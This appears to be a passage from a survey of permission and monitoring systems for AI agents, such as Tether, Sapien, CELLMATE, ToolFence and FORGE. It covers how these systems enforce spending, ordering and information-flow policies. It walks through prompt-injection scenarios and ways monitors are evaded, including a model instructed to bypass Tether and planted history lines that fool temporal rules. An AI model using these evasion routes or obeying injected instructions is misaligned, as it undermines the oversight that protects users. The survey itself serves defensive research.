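Zhu and colleagues tested MiniScope on synthetic requests for ten real applications, including Gmail, Slack and Dropbox. When language models chose the permission scopes instead of MiniScope's solver, proprietary models found the minimal set in 70–83% of cases and open models in 20–34%. The solver's choices are minimal by definition, so these figures measure only how often a model agrees with that definition. The solver also identified six real connectors (ready-made links between an assistant and a service) that had more permissions than they needed. MiniScope added at most 7% to the running time. In a simulation of three months of Gmail use, 18% to 60% of requests needed the user's confirmation, depending on the type of user.

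In the paper's main example, a user asks the assistant to reply to an email about an event. The email contains a planted instruction to delete it after replying. The agent has read-only access at first, but its new plan includes sending and deleting, so MiniScope prompts the user to approve full access to Gmail. The user notices the unexpected deletion step and refuses. The refusal blocks the reply along with the attack, because the request combined permission to send with permission to delete.

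If the planted instruction had instead told the assistant to copy the reply to a stranger, the user would have seen an ordinary request for permission to send. Zhu and colleagues state that MiniScope doesn't protect against changed arguments or extra calls within an approved scope. MiniScope can limit an assistant to sending, but it can't enforce the rule *write only to people in my contacts*.

### Describing what a tool does

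*AC4A* (2026) presents an access-control system that attaches permissions to resources instead of tool calls. The resources form a hierarchy, so a permission could cover one calendar and its events. For each application, someone writes functions that map a call's operation and arguments to the permissions the call requires. These functions allow distinctions that the provider's scopes lack. The same permissions apply whether the agent uses an API or web pages.

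In case studies with Outlook Calendar and Expedia, agents worked within restricted permissions, and AC4A blocked actions outside them. The case studies show that the approach can work with real applications, but they don't measure how often it makes mistakes. The protection depends on handwritten functions that identify which resource a call affects. If a function returns the family calendar for a call that changes the work calendar, the monitor will check the call against the user's rule for the wrong calendar.

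Every monitor relies on some description of this kind, even if it is only the tool's name. Suppose the description of an assistant's `summarise_file` tool lists only reading a file. If the tool also sends the text to another company's server for processing, a call on the medical folder breaks the fourth policy but looks like a harmless read. In terms of the condition above, the real set of effects is larger than the one the monitor checked. The opposite mistake, listing an effect the tool can't have, makes the monitor block permitted work.

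A correct description of a tool can also go out of date. If the supplier later changes the tool to send files to an outside server, its name and arguments may stay the same. The user's rule would then still allow the call, even though the user approved it when the tool worked differently.

Zhou and Zhang suggest giving each tool an effect contract, which lists the resources the tool may access, what data it may send and to whom, and what it may change elsewhere. Developers could prepare these contracts by analysing the tool's code, running it in an isolated environment and watching its network traffic. Comparing the results between versions could reveal new effects. This is a research proposal, and it is weakest for outside services, whose code the user can't inspect. A trial run shows what the tool sent to the service and what came back, but not whether the service passed the data on.

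### The same rule over typed tools and a shell

A typed tool, such as `send_mail(to, subject, body)`, has a fixed set of named arguments, while a shell accepts any command as a line of text. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026) describes a coding agent with both kinds. Its read, write and edit tools each take a file path, which a monitor can look up in a list. Its shell tool takes a single string, from which the monitor has to work out which files the command will open and where it will send them.

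*Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) uses file uploads to show how the shape of a tool limits what can be blocked. A company's server inventory is in `data/servers.csv`, and a harmless status report is in `scratch/report.txt`. The agent may read the inventory and may upload the report to GitHub, but the inventory must not leave the machine. The agent uploads the report, overwrites it with the inventory, and uploads `scratch/report.txt` again. The two upload commands are identical, but a monitor should allow the first and block the second.

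The researchers wrote a rule to block the upload of any file that the agent has copied from the inventory and not rewritten since. The rule is in Dogwood, an Amazon policy language that can refer to earlier calls. It can block these uploads when the agent has a typed tool for copying, because each copy then appears in the log with its source and destination.

When the agent has only a shell, the log contains command strings. Dogwood can match a past command by its exact text but can't extract a file name from it, so the rule has to quote the expected command, `cp data/servers.csv scratch/report.txt`. If the agent runs `cat data/servers.csv > scratch/report.txt` instead, it gets the same result, but the rule doesn't match. The shell version also doesn't check whether the agent has since replaced the report with harmless text, so it would block a harmless upload.

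The typed rule isn't exact either. By default it looks back only 24 hours, and it misses an inventory that reaches the report through a third file. It could also miss an agent that reads the inventory and writes the contents into the report itself, because the rule treats any rewriting as making the report safe. A second rule can cover a two-step copy, and a third can cover a three-step copy. These rules work only because typed calls name the files. With a generic shell tool, Dogwood can't express even the two-step rule.

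### Tether: observing a command's effects

Tether, the system that Sistla and colleagues built at Google, doesn't try to predict a command's effects from its text. It handles each command as follows:

1. It runs the command on a disposable layer over the file system, so that changes to files don't yet affect the real ones.
2. It records the command's system calls, the requests that a program makes to the operating system to open a file or use the network. A local proxy holds any outgoing web request.
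3. It translates the recorded calls into 11 general actions, such as read, copy, delete and upload.
4. It checks these actions against the policy. If the policy allows them all, Tether applies the changes to the real files and releases the web requests. Otherwise it discards them.

The `cp` and `cat` commands both open the inventory, read it and write to the report, so Tether records each as a copy. It also marks the report as sensitive after the copy, which is a form of tracking information between calls. One short rule that allows uploads only of public files then blocks the second upload, however many copies the agent makes.

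System calls show which files a program read and wrote, but not what it did with the data in between. If a script reads one file and then writes another, Tether treats the second as containing data from the first, even if the script only counted the lines. α requires Tether to err in this direction, but doing so causes false alarms. For example, searching all files with `grep -r` opens the secret ones too, so Tether treats the agent as having read the secrets and blocks its later actions.

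The researchers compared Tether with Auto Mode, a feature of Anthropic's Claude Code in which a model reviews each command. They replayed recorded runs from two benchmarks for coding agents. Some runs contained only a normal task, while others also had a hidden harmful one.

| Monitor | Harmful runs blocked | Harmless runs wrongly blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Tether | 344 of 344 | 4.7% |
| Auto Mode, default rules | 91.6% | 9.7% |
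| Auto Mode, given Tether's policy | 89.2% | 3.5% |

Auto Mode missed attacks inside scripts, whose behaviour isn't visible on the command line. When it had Tether's policy, it blocked fewer harmless runs than Tether did, but it was inconsistent about which web addresses the policy allowed.

Tether's perfect score covers only runs whose actions it could trace and model, which excludes background jobs and database queries. Sistla and colleagues also refined the policy by testing it on benchmark runs, so Tether may do worse on new tasks. They judged that 28.2% of the runs left out of the main test on one benchmark, and 22.1% on the other, required an understanding of content. For instance, an agent that puts harmful code in a file it is allowed to edit produces the same system calls as one that writes good code.

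In a further test, the researchers told a model to get around the monitor. It succeeded in 40% of attempts against an early version and in none against the third, after the researchers had fixed gaps such as overlooked hard links, which give one file a second name. Each gap was an error in translating system calls into actions. The policy's rules were correct throughout, and Sistla and colleagues had machine-checked proofs about them, but those proofs apply only if the translation is right.

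For a personal assistant, Tether's method covers only what happens on the user's machine. It can show that a program sent a request to a payment service, and the proxy may record the request's contents, but not what the service did next. The prototype also decrypts secure web traffic only for simulated services, although Sistla and colleagues say a different proxy could extend this to real ones.

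### CELLMATE: giving meaning to clicks

Many websites offer no API for the task a user wants done, so some assistants operate a browser as a person would. *From Language Models to World-Acting Systems* (Zhu and Cai, 2026) describes this as trading explicit meaning for reach. An API call specifies an operation and its arguments, whereas a browser lets the assistant press almost any visible button but gives much less information about what the button will do.

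A rule about clicks can't enforce a policy such as *never delete mail*, because the same click might open a message on one page and delete it on another, and the positions of buttons change with the size of the window. Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025) found in *CELLMATE* that an agent can also get around a block on the browser's navigation tool. When they prevented an agent from going directly to Hacker News, it searched for the site on DuckDuckGo and clicked the result.

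CELLMATE is a Chrome extension that checks HTTP requests, the messages a browser sends to a website. Whichever button the agent presses to place an order on Amazon, the browser has to send a request to the same part of the site. The website's developers list such requests and their meanings in a file called an agent sitemap, and policies refer to the meanings:

| Request | Meaning | Example policy |
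|---|---|---|
| open the cart page | `ViewCart` | allow |
| send a change to the cart | `UpdateCart` | allow |
| submit the order | `PlaceOrder` | allow if the total is at most $50 |

Amazon's order request doesn't include the total. To let the monitor enforce the limit on it, the sitemap also specifies where the total appears on the checkout page, and the extension saves it before the page closes. If the agent changes a quantity and orders before the page has updated, the monitor could check an old total. CELLMATE reduces this risk by slowing down the agent's actions. Like the museum token, the rule also needs a limit on the number of purchases.

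A language model uses the user's request to choose from a set of ready-made policies, fills in values such as the $50, and shows the result to the user for confirmation. Like Conseca's policy writer, it reads no untrusted content while doing this. The best models chose and filled in the policies with an overall accuracy above 94% in every task category. With suitable policies, CELLMATE blocked the prompt-injection attacks in the WASP benchmark. It increased the agent's running time by 7.25–15%.

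The approach depends on websites publishing sitemaps and keeping them current. Meng and colleagues wrote one themselves for 51 operations on GitLab, a site for software projects. They argue that developers already maintain similar files and have an interest in protecting their users. If a sitemap is missing an entry, the agent is about as free there as it would be without CELLMATE. To enforce *write only to people in my contacts*, a user also needs the mail site's developers to list the recipients as something a policy can check.

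Zhu and Cai recommend that assistants use structured calls where these are adequate and the browser only when necessary, with the same policies applying to both. Otherwise, an assistant can use the browser to bypass the controls on the mail tool.

### What deployed assistants let users restrict

Zhu and colleagues describe how several products asked for permission in December 2025. Users who connected Gmail or Slack to ChatGPT or Claude approved a predefined set of permissions once, and later calls ran without further approval. When users added their own tool servers to Claude, it showed the function and arguments of every call and waited for approval. Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, ran low-risk operations automatically and asked for approval of high-risk ones such as network access. Companies change these settings often, so current products may differ.

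The first two arrangements differ greatly in how much of the seven example policies they can cover.

| Policy | Permissions approved once | Approval of every call |
|---|---|---|
| Never delete mail | only if the user can leave out deletion | the user refuses each deletion |
| Write only to contacts | no | the user checks each recipient |
| At most $200 this month | no | only if the user keeps a running total |
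| Nothing leaves from the medical folder | only by not connecting the folder | only if the user recognises where the text came from |
| Ask before anything irreversible | no | yes, but it also asks about everything else |
| Answer the school within a day | no | no, and waiting for approval may cause a delay |
| Send nothing embarrassing | no | the user judges each message |

Approving every call covers more policies than a one-time permission because the user sees each call's arguments. But the user has to apply the policies by hand every time, and Zhu and colleagues warn that constant questions lead to decision fatigue. Codex comes closest to *ask me before anything that cannot be undone*, since it asks about some actions and not others. But its categories are based on risk, and whether an action uses the network is a poor guide to whether it can be undone. For example, looking up a train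 time uses the network but changes nothing, while deleting the only copy of a photograph is permanent and doesn't need the network.

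## Spending limits, ordering rules and other policies that depend on the past

Suppose the user tries to enforce *spend at most $200 this month* with a rule that allows any purchase of up to $50. The assistant then makes five $50 purchases, which each satisfy the rule but together cost $250. A lower limit would only raise the number of purchases needed to break the policy. Conditions on the payee or the item don't help either, because the fifth purchase can be identical to the first.

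*Local Allow, Global Deny* (2026) describes a general weakness of checking actions one at a time. Each action can pass its check while the run as a whole violates what the user authorised. This can happen without an attacker. In an early trial for *Compromise Is Not Consequence* (2026), an agent made a legitimate payment twice. Its permission specified the action and the resource but not how many times the agent could use it.

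To enforce the monthly limit, the monitor has to keep a total:

```
allow pay(amount)   when   spent this month + amount ≤ 200
```

After four purchases of $50 the total is $200, so the monitor blocks the fifth. Other history-dependent policies require other kinds of memory.

| Type | Example | What the monitor must store |
|---|---|---|
| Budget | spend at most $200 this month | the total so far |
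| One-time use | buy one museum ticket | whether the purchase has happened |
| Required order | read an invoice before paying it | which invoices the assistant has read |
| "Not after" | send no mail after opening the medical folder | whether the assistant has opened the folder |
| Separation of duties | the helper that chooses a plumber can't approve the bill | which helper took each earlier step |

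A system can keep this memory in the token that the assistant presents or in a central monitor.

### Memory in the token: HCAP

Tandon, Fong and Safavi-Naini (2018), in *HCAP*, designed tokens with memory for smart locks and other connected devices. In their main example, Alice works late and leaves through the lab door, the building entrance and the campus gate, in that order. If her phone tries to open the campus gate first, someone outside may have picked it up. The rule is a small state machine, which lists the operations permitted in each state and the state that follows each operation:

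```
in lab  --lab door-->  in building  --entrance-->  on campus  --gate-->  outside
```

Alice's token specifies the current state and contains a fragment of the machine. When she unlocks the lab door, the lock finds the operation in the fragment, opens, computes the next state and gives her a new token for that state. The lock doesn't need a copy of the policy in advance, and it usually doesn't need to contact the central server that issued the first token.

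Alice could keep a copy of the old token and reuse it, so the lock also records when the state last changed and rejects any token from before that time. Tandon and colleagues prove that the devices and the server together allow exactly what a single central monitor running the same machine would allow, and that someone who loses a token can get a working one again. The proofs assume that the devices and the server are trustworthy, that their clocks agree, and that nobody can extract their secret keys.

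Keeping everything synchronized adds delay. If the token's fragment doesn't describe the next state, the lock gives Alice a signed record of what she has done, which she has to take to the central server for a new token. Larger fragments make this rarer but produce larger tokens. On a fast wired network, requests took 5.5 milliseconds on average when none involved the central server and 12.3 milliseconds when all of them did. When Alice moves to a different lock, that lock has to contact the previous one, which validates her token and hands over its record of the session. When every request required a handover, each took about 60 milliseconds if the record kept growing, and about 6 milliseconds after the researchers removed loops from it.

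HCAP can limit a visitor to four cups from a smart coffee machine, but it is poorly suited to spending limits. Its permissions specify an operation and a resource, not an amount, and its state machines need a separate state for every possible total. A $200 limit counted in cents would take 20,001 states. In one test, a state machine with 13 densely connected states was too large to send in a single network packet.

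A more basic obstacle for a personal assistant is that mail and payment services would have to read these tokens and issue new ones, which today's services don't do.

### Memory in a monitor: Sapien

A monitor that sees every call can keep the history itself, without cooperation from the services. *Sapien* (Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) describes such a monitor, built at Google. As in Conseca, a language model writes a policy for each task, but a Sapien policy is a pattern for the whole sequence of calls. The policy can also store the result of one call and use it to check the arguments of another.

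In the main example, the user tells the assistant to do the tasks on a to-do list at `todo.io/bob`. The policy writer can't know what the list contains, so it permits one call and leaves a gap:

```
get_page(url="todo.io/bob")@todo . defer(gen_todo)
```

The dot means "and then", and `@todo` stores the page under the name `todo`. `defer` marks the gap. Suppose the page asks the assistant to forward Acme's invoice to the accounting department and to email Alice a summary of `notes.md`. Sapien passes these tasks to the policy writer and puts the resulting pattern in the gap. In simplified form, it is:

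```
( read_email@emails* . forward_email(to accounting, an Acme message in emails) )
||
( read_file("notes.md")@notes . send_email(to Alice, a summary of notes) )
```

The star allows any number of repetitions, and `||` lets the assistant mix the steps of the two tasks as long as it keeps each task's own order. The assistant can read any number of emails but forward only one, which must come from Acme and be among those it has read. Ordinary code checks these conditions. Whether the message to Alice is a faithful summary is a semantic predicate, which Sapien checks by having a language model answer a yes-or-no question. If hidden text in the notes causes that model to answer wrongly, the assistant can still send only one message, and only to Alice.

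Sometimes the history doesn't show which task an action belongs to. Suppose one task is to forward Acme's invoice, another is to answer Bob's question, and both begin with a search of the inbox. The assistant searches for "Bob" and then for "Acme". Sapien keeps both ways of matching the searches to the tasks. When the assistant forwards a message from the second search, that search must belong to the forwarding task, so Sapien discards the other matching. The reply to Bob then has to match the results of the first search.

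The gap in the policy addresses the problem Conseca had when an email defined the task. The policy writer reads outside text only when the user has told the assistant to follow it. This doesn't make the text safe, because anyone who can edit the to-do list can add a task, and Sapien will write a policy that permits it.

Tiffany and colleagues tested Sapien with four models on AgentDojo and on Toolathlon, a benchmark of 108 longer tasks with more than 600 tools. On AgentDojo, agents completed one to five fewer of the 97 tasks with a policy than without one. On Toolathlon, where only Gemini 3.8 Flash ran the full set, the success rate with a policy was within 4% of the rate without one.

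In the security test, the researchers assumed that the attacker already controlled the agent and could fool any model that read untrusted text. They then looked for any sequence of permitted calls that would achieve the attacker's goal. This is stricter than the usual test, which counts how often an injection works. On AgentDojo, Sapien's policies ruled out 93.2–95.2% of 949 attacks, compared with 82.7–86.8% for a simple list of permitted tools. On Toolathlon, they ruled out 64.6% of 212 attacks, compared with 32.4% for the list. The gap is wider on Toolathlon because the researchers wrote attacks that misuse tools the task needs, and a list of permitted tools can't stop those. Most of the attacks that remained possible did harm through the wording of a message, a file or the agent's answer.

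Sapien is slow, mainly because writing a policy takes time. The average AgentDojo task took 66 to 144 seconds with Sapien, depending on the model, and 12 to 62 seconds without a policy.

A Sapien policy also lasts for only one task. It can require the assistant to read an invoice before paying it, but it has no record of what the assistant spent last week.

### Rules in temporal logic

An alternative to writing a new pattern for every task is a general rule about the past, such as "no deletion without an earlier approval". Temporal logic, which extends ordinary logic with terms for time, can express this precisely:

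```
□ ∀a. ( destructive(a) → ◆ approved(a) )
```

The box means "at every moment" and the diamond means "at some earlier moment". *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues, 2026) gives five rules of this form, covering deletion, switching off protections, payments, sending data out, and changing settings or devices. The researchers applied the rules to recorded runs from AgentDojo and from STAC, a collection of 483 attacks in which a series of harmless-looking calls leads up to a harmful one. No agent ran during the study, so the results show which runs the rules would have flagged, but not how an agent would have reacted to a block.

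The rules flagged 71.8% of the STAC attacks and 70.1% of the successful AgentDojo attacks on GPT-4o. They also flagged 29.3% of the AgentDojo runs that contained no attack. At these rates, if 10 of an assistant's 1,000 tasks involved a successful attack, the monitor would raise about seven correct alarms and 290 false ones.

The problem is mostly with the recordings. In AgentDojo the user gives only one instruction, at the start, so no approval can follow a proposed action. The formula above therefore flags every deletion, and a list of forbidden words would work just as well. A rule about approvals would have something to check in τ-bench, a predecessor of the customer-service benchmark τ²-bench, because the user had given explicit permission before a change in 52.5% of 1,980 recorded runs.

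Rules that used more of the history did better. For AgentDojo's banking tasks, the researchers replaced "flag every payment" with "flag a payment to anyone who doesn't appear in the earlier account data". The share of harmless runs flagged fell from 44% to 24%, while the share of attacks detected fell from 79.2% to 70.0%.

However, an attacker can write part of the history that such a rule relies on. When the researchers added one line to each flagged run presenting the attacker's account as an existing payee, the rule accepted 94% of the payments it had flagged before. A similar line defeated the corresponding rule for email recipients in 99% of cases. The attack did not need to fool a model, because the monitor itself treated the planted line as a genuine record.

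The fix was to trust an account number only if it came in the reply to a lookup the agent had made. With this change, the planted lines never succeeded, and the rule flagged as many attacks and as many harmless runs as before. An attacker who controls the tool that answers the lookup could still get around the rule. Sapien's stored results are similar because each name refers to the reply to a particular call, but a forged invoice in the inbox is still part of a genuine reply.

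Temporal logic can also measure time, which is necessary for a monthly limit. In one of the study's examples, the monitor allows a data export if the user consented 12 hours earlier and flags it if the consent is 48 hours old. Kekatos and colleagues wrote the logs for these examples themselves because none of the three attack and safety benchmarks they examined records the time of a call.

### Two agents and one purchase

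Suppose the user wants one museum ticket, and the assistant asks two helpers to look for it, one on the museum's website and one at a ticket agency. The assistant has permission to buy one ticket and gives each helper a token for one purchase. Neither token permits more than the assistant itself may do, so this is proper attenuation. But if both helpers find a ticket and buy it, the user ends up with two.

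The assistant could give the permission to only one helper, but then the other can't buy a ticket even if it finds a cheaper one. Similarly, if each helper gets half of a $200 budget, neither can make a $120 purchase, even when nothing has been spent. To avoid this, the helpers have to share a counter that tracks their total spending.

A shared counter can still fail if checking it and changing it are separate steps:

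| Step | First helper | Second helper | Purchases left |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | checks the counter | | 1 |
| 2 | | checks the counter | 1 |
| 3 | buys a ticket | | 0 |
| 4 | | buys a ticket | −1 |

Both checks were correct when the helpers made them. The monitor has to check the counter and reserve the purchase in one step that nothing can interrupt, so that the second helper finds the counter at zero.

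Checking the total only occasionally causes a similar problem. *Safety Does Not Compose* (2026) calculates how far an agent can overshoot a limit if the monitor checks its count only between pieces of work. With a limit of B and up to m actions in each piece, the count can reach B + m − 1. If the limit is four purchases and the assistant can make three between checks, it could pass a check after three purchases and then make three more, for a total of six.

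Li, Cao and Xiao (2026), in *ToolFence*, combine the check with a reservation. A model that sees only the user's request and trusted tool descriptions turns the request into capabilities. Each one specifies a tool, where its sensitive arguments may come from, and how many times the agent may use it. For each capability, the monitor counts the uses that are free and those it is holding for calls in progress:

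| Event | Free | Held |
|---|---|---|
| Before the call | 1 | 0 |
| The monitor reserves the use | 0 | 1 |
| The payment succeeds | 0 | 0 |
| Or the payment definitely fails | 1 | 0 |
| Or the outcome is unknown | 0 | 1 |

Li and colleagues measured how much each check adds, using proposed calls from AgentDojo's banking tasks. When the monitor checked only the tool, it accepted 89.3% of unauthorised calls. Adding a check on the source of the arguments reduced this to 84.5%, adding one on the stage of the task reduced it to 45.2%, and adding the limit on uses reduced it to 6.0%. The monitor accepted every legitimate call with each combination of checks. The researchers had added calls at the wrong stage and repeats of calls that had already used up their budget, so the size of each drop partly reflects the mix of calls they chose.

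In the full AgentDojo test with the model Qwen3-max, ToolFence reduced attack success from 21.2% to zero, while task completion without attacks fell from 66.3% to 64.3%. On AgentLAB, whose attacks unfold over many steps, 29.4% still succeeded, down from 76.3%. Some of those attacks made a harmful action look like a necessary part of the task, which no counter can detect.

ToolFence counts uses, which also limits the money when the request fixes the price. If prices vary, the monitor has to reserve an amount:

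```
allow pay(amount)   when   spent + held + amount ≤ 200
```

Suppose the assistant has spent $150, and the monitor is holding $40 for a train booking that is still going through. The monitor will block Mia's $18 school fee because it would bring the total to $208. If the booking then fails, the block will have been unnecessary, but the monitor had to allow or block the fee before the booking's outcome was known.

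### Retries that buy twice

Agent libOS doesn't automatically resend a payment call that gets no response, because the money may already have moved. *Verified Tool Calls Improve LLM Agent Reliability Under Non-Atomic Failures* (2026) points out that methods for teaching agents to retry after an error assume that the first attempt had no effect.

An agent can repeat an action even if it checks before retrying. *Where Does Exactly-Once Live?* (2026) includes a run in which Claude Opus 5.5 had to announce a software release on LinkedIn. Its call to publish the post timed out. The agent listed the account's recent posts, then published the announcement again. But the original request was still in progress and took effect later, so the announcement appeared twice. The agent reported that it had completed the task.

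The usual remedy is an idempotency key, a unique label sent with a request. If the service receives a second request with the same key, it doesn't repeat the action. In another run in that paper, the agent attached such a key to a post, so it could safely retry without checking. Keys work only if the service supports them. Otherwise the monitor can keep the use on hold, as ToolFence does, until someone finds out what happened. That prevents a second purchase, but it may leave the user without a ticket.

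A monitor might instead try to recognise duplicates by comparing each call with earlier ones. That works for ordinary programs, which usually send exactly the same request again. A language model writes each call afresh and may word it differently:

```
buy(item="museum ticket, child, Saturday", amount=12)
buy(item="Child admission (Sat)", amount=12)
```

These calls have different text, so a simple comparison treats them as two purchases. A key calculated from the text would also differ, and a key that the model makes up for each attempt might too. A looser comparison, such as one of only the shop and the price, would block a parent who wants tickets for two children.

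The harness can avoid the problem by creating the key itself when the monitor reserves the purchase. Every attempt under that reservation then carries the same key, whatever the model writes. To buy a second ticket, the assistant would need another reservation, which it can get only if the budget allows.

### Forbidden combinations and split sessions

Some policies forbid a combination of actions that are each harmless on their own. For example, a user might let an assistant read confidential files and send mail to outsiders, but not both in the same task. *Bounded Agents* (Muruaga, 2026) describes a monitor that sorts every tool into a type of action, such as "read" or "send externally", and records which types the agents in a session have used. It blocks any call that would complete a forbidden pair. Because the agents share one record, they can't avoid the rule by having one read a file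 and another send it.

Muruaga proves that if every outcome the user wants to prevent requires some forbidden pair, then no sequence of permitted calls can produce such an outcome. To produce one, the agents would have to use both types in the pair, and when one of them tried the second, the monitor would find the first on its list and refuse the call.

The result requires the list of forbidden pairs to cover every unwanted outcome, the monitor to decide on calls one at a time, and the list to stay the same during the session. With the full list, the monitor blocked all 544 data-theft attacks in InjecAgent. After Muruaga removed one pair, 39.9% of the attacks succeeded.

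Rules that forbid pairs also miss violations that take more steps. An agent could read a confidential file, copy its contents into a shared document and then send that document to a colleague, without completing a forbidden pair. Muruaga adds rules for ordered sequences of three or more types to catch this.

These rules are coarse because they track whether the assistant has read something confidential, not where the contents went. If the user forbids sending mail after opening the medical folder, an assistant that has opened it can't email a friend to confirm lunch for the rest of the session, even if the message contains nothing medical. On AgentDojo under attack, agents' completion rate for the user's tasks was 8.6 percentage points lower with the full set of checks when a simulated user could approve sensitive actions, and 13.9 points lower when nobody could.

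Muruaga also proves that an agent's reach can never exceed that of the agent that delegated to it, because everything the first agent has already used counts against the second agent's budget. This result applies only along a single chain of delegation. Suppose an assistant has spent $50 of its $200 and then delegates to two helpers. Each helper starts with $50 counted as spent and $150 left. The theorem still holds if both helpers spend all $150, bringing the total to $350. To prevent that, the helpers' spending has to go into the same record.

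The guarantee about combinations ends with the session. In one of Muruaga's tests, an agent read a file in one session and sent it in another, and the monitor allowed it. An assistant can do this without any bad intent if the user starts a new conversation between the two steps. The other systems have similar limits. A Sapien policy and a ToolFence budget each apply to one task, and HCAP starts a new state machine for each session.

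A limit of $200 a month therefore needs a record that no agent can reset by restarting. *Bounded Autonomy* (2026) applies this principle to computing costs by giving each part of a task a single allowance of model use, which the agent can't renew by retrying, restarting, changing its plan or taking on a new identity. For money, the user could get much the same effect from a prepaid card that receives $200 on the first of each month. The card's issuer keeps one balance for every agent and every session, and reserves the money when it authorises a payment. The issuer can't tell a duplicate ticket from one the user wanted, but the total stays within $200 as long as the assistant has no other way to pay.

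## Policies on where information may go

Enforcing the fourth example policy, *nothing from my medical folder leaves my accounts*, requires a record of what the assistant has read, whereas a prepaid card can enforce a spending limit without one. Suppose the user asks the assistant to book a doctor's appointment and to answer Mia's school. Booking the appointment requires permission to read the medical folder, and answering the school requires permission to write to its office. Each permission is proper on its own, but together they let the assistant email the school something from the folder.

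In *Paradigm Regained*, Miller and Shapiro distinguish permission from authority. A program has permission to use the objects it can reach directly. Its authority also includes what it can do with the help of other programs. If Alice has permission to read a file and sends copies of it to Bob, Bob has authority to read the file without permission. The assistant could likewise give the school authority to read a file by sending it copies.

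Forbidding all mail once the assistant has opened the folder would prevent this, but it would also block the harmless message about lunch. To block only messages that would reveal the folder's contents, the monitor has to track where those contents have gone.

### Labels for secrecy and trust

Information-flow control attaches labels to data and carries them along as a program uses the data. A confidentiality label records who may read the data, and an integrity label records whether it came from a trusted source. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes Fides, a system built at Microsoft that keeps both labels on everything an agent handles.

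When a result depends on two pieces of data, it takes the stricter label of each kind:

```
readers(result)  =  readers(x) ∩ readers(y)
result is trusted   only if   x and y are both trusted
```

The assistant's reply to the school might get its labels like this:

| Data | Who may read it | Trusted? |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request | anyone | yes |
| The school's message | the user and the school | no |
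| `medical/allergies.txt` | the user | yes |
| The reply, which depends on all three | the user | no |

In an ordinary program, a tracker can follow each variable separately. But a language model computes each word from its whole context, and nobody can reliably tell which parts influenced that word. The cautious solution is to treat everything the model writes as if it depended on everything the model has read.

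Fides's basic policy has two rules. The agent may send data only to recipients whom the labels allow to read it, and it may not take a consequential action while its context contains untrusted data. The first rule enforces the medical policy by blocking the reply, since the school isn't among the reply's permitted readers. The second protects against injected instructions, but it also blocks the $18 payment because the assistant has read the school's message.

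### Release and endorsement

If these rules had no exceptions, the assistant could not tell the school about the allergy or pay the fee. Information-flow systems therefore allow two kinds of controlled exception. Zhou and Zhang define declassification as a policy-authorised release of restricted data, and endorsement as permission for less trusted data to influence a protected decision.

To release information, the user could approve the sentence "Mia is allergic to peanuts" for the school office. The monitor would then add the office to that sentence's permitted readers. Approving exact words matters because the model would choose what to take from the folder if the user instead released "whatever the school needs to know".

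An endorsement could let the assistant use the fee in the school's message without trusting the rest of the message. Fides can base such exceptions on a value's type, such as a number or a yes-or-no answer, since values of these types can't contain an instruction. But they can still cause harm. In Zhou and Zhang's example, a source may answer only "yes" or "no" when asked whether a draft is approved for external release. A false "yes" could release the whole draft, so the system also has to check whether that source has the right to approve it.

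### The dispute over capabilities and secrecy

Labels are one way to stop secrets from spreading. An older question is whether capabilities alone can do it. Military computer security used two rules to contain secrets. A program may read only data at or below its own clearance, and may write only to places at or above it. The second rule, called the star property, prevents a program that has read a secret from copying it to a less secret place.

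In 1984 Boebert argued that an unmodified capability machine can't enforce the star property. By "unmodified" he meant that capabilities are the machine's only control on access to stored data. Miller and colleagues reconstruct his example. Alice is a program with low clearance and Bob is one with high clearance. Each can use two areas of memory, Low and High, as far as the rules permit:

| Program | Low | High |
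|---|---|---|
| Alice | read, write | write |
| Bob | read | read, write |

The attack takes four steps:

1. Alice writes a copy of her capability to write to Low into Low itself.
2. Bob reads Low, as his clearance permits, and obtains the capability.
3. Bob reads a secret from High and uses the capability to write it into Low.
4. Alice reads the secret.

Alice, not the system, gave Bob permission to write to Low, and every step used a capability that its holder really had. Later researchers took the argument as proof that capability systems in general can't keep information confined.

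Miller and colleagues accept that the attack works on the machine Boebert described, but object that it assumes a capability can travel wherever data can. Most capability systems store the two differently, so a program needs one permission to read data from a memory area and another to read capabilities from it, and likewise for writing. Suppose the system gives out permissions to read and write capabilities only within a level. Alice can still put her capability into Low, but Bob can read only the data there, so the second step fails. Alice can't pass it to him through High either, because she can write only data to High. Bob never gains a way to write to the lower level, and the star property holds.

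Whether confinement is possible therefore depends on what a capability is. If a program can copy a capability and give it to any other program, confinement is impossible. In what Miller and colleagues call the object-capability model, a program can pass a capability to another only if it already has a capability to communicate with that program. Miller and Shapiro summarise this principle as "only connectivity begets connectivity", meaning that programs that start with no path between them can't create one.

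In 2015 Jerry Leichter complained on a cryptography mailing list that Miller and colleagues answer objections to capabilities by extending the capability model. This is partly fair, since their reply to Boebert adds a distinction between capabilities and ordinary data that his example lacks. But nearly all capability systems already made this distinction, and a machine that makes it still meets Boebert's own definition, because it uses only capabilities to control access. Miller and colleagues also concede that Boebert's result applies to systems that can't make the distinction, although designers have found ways around the problem in some of these.

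That concession matters for assistants because a model that can read a bearer token can paste it into an email, just as Alice wrote her capability into Low. Keeping tokens in the harness prevents this.

The reply doesn't solve the problem with the medical folder. It protects High by ensuring that Bob, who can read secrets, cannot write to Low, but an assistant that must read the folder and write to the school needs both permissions from the start. The user could split the work between two assistants, one that can read the folder but has no outside contact and another that can use mail but cannot read the folder. This enforces the policy, but neither assistant can tell the school about the allergy.

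### FORGE: tracing what influenced an action

*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* introduces FORGE, a monitor that keeps both permissions in one system and checks what each action depends on. FORGE records every message, tool call and tool result as an event in a graph, with an arrow from each event to the later ones it may have influenced. When a model writes a message, FORGE draws an arrow to it from every message in the history that the model received. Before an action with outside effects, FORGE follows the arrows backwards to find what may have influenced that action.

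The main example has seven events. The labels in the last column follow from the rules given below the table.

| Event | What happens | Labels |
|---|---|---|
| v0 | a system message sets up the agent | |
| v1 | the user asks for a summary of a vendor's document | |
| v2 | the agent calls the tool to read it | |
| v3 | the file system returns the document, which contains an injected instruction | tainted |
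| v4 | the agent calls the tool to read a sensitive internal file | tainted |
| v5 | the file system returns the sensitive contents | tainted, secret |
| v6 | the agent tries to email an outside address | tainted, secret |

In plain notation, the policy is:

```
tainted(x)   if   x is untrusted input
tainted(x)   if   x depends on some y, and tainted(y)

secret(x)    if   x is sensitive input
secret(x)    if   x depends on some y, and secret(y)

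block(a)     if   a sends something outside, and tainted(a), and secret(a)
```

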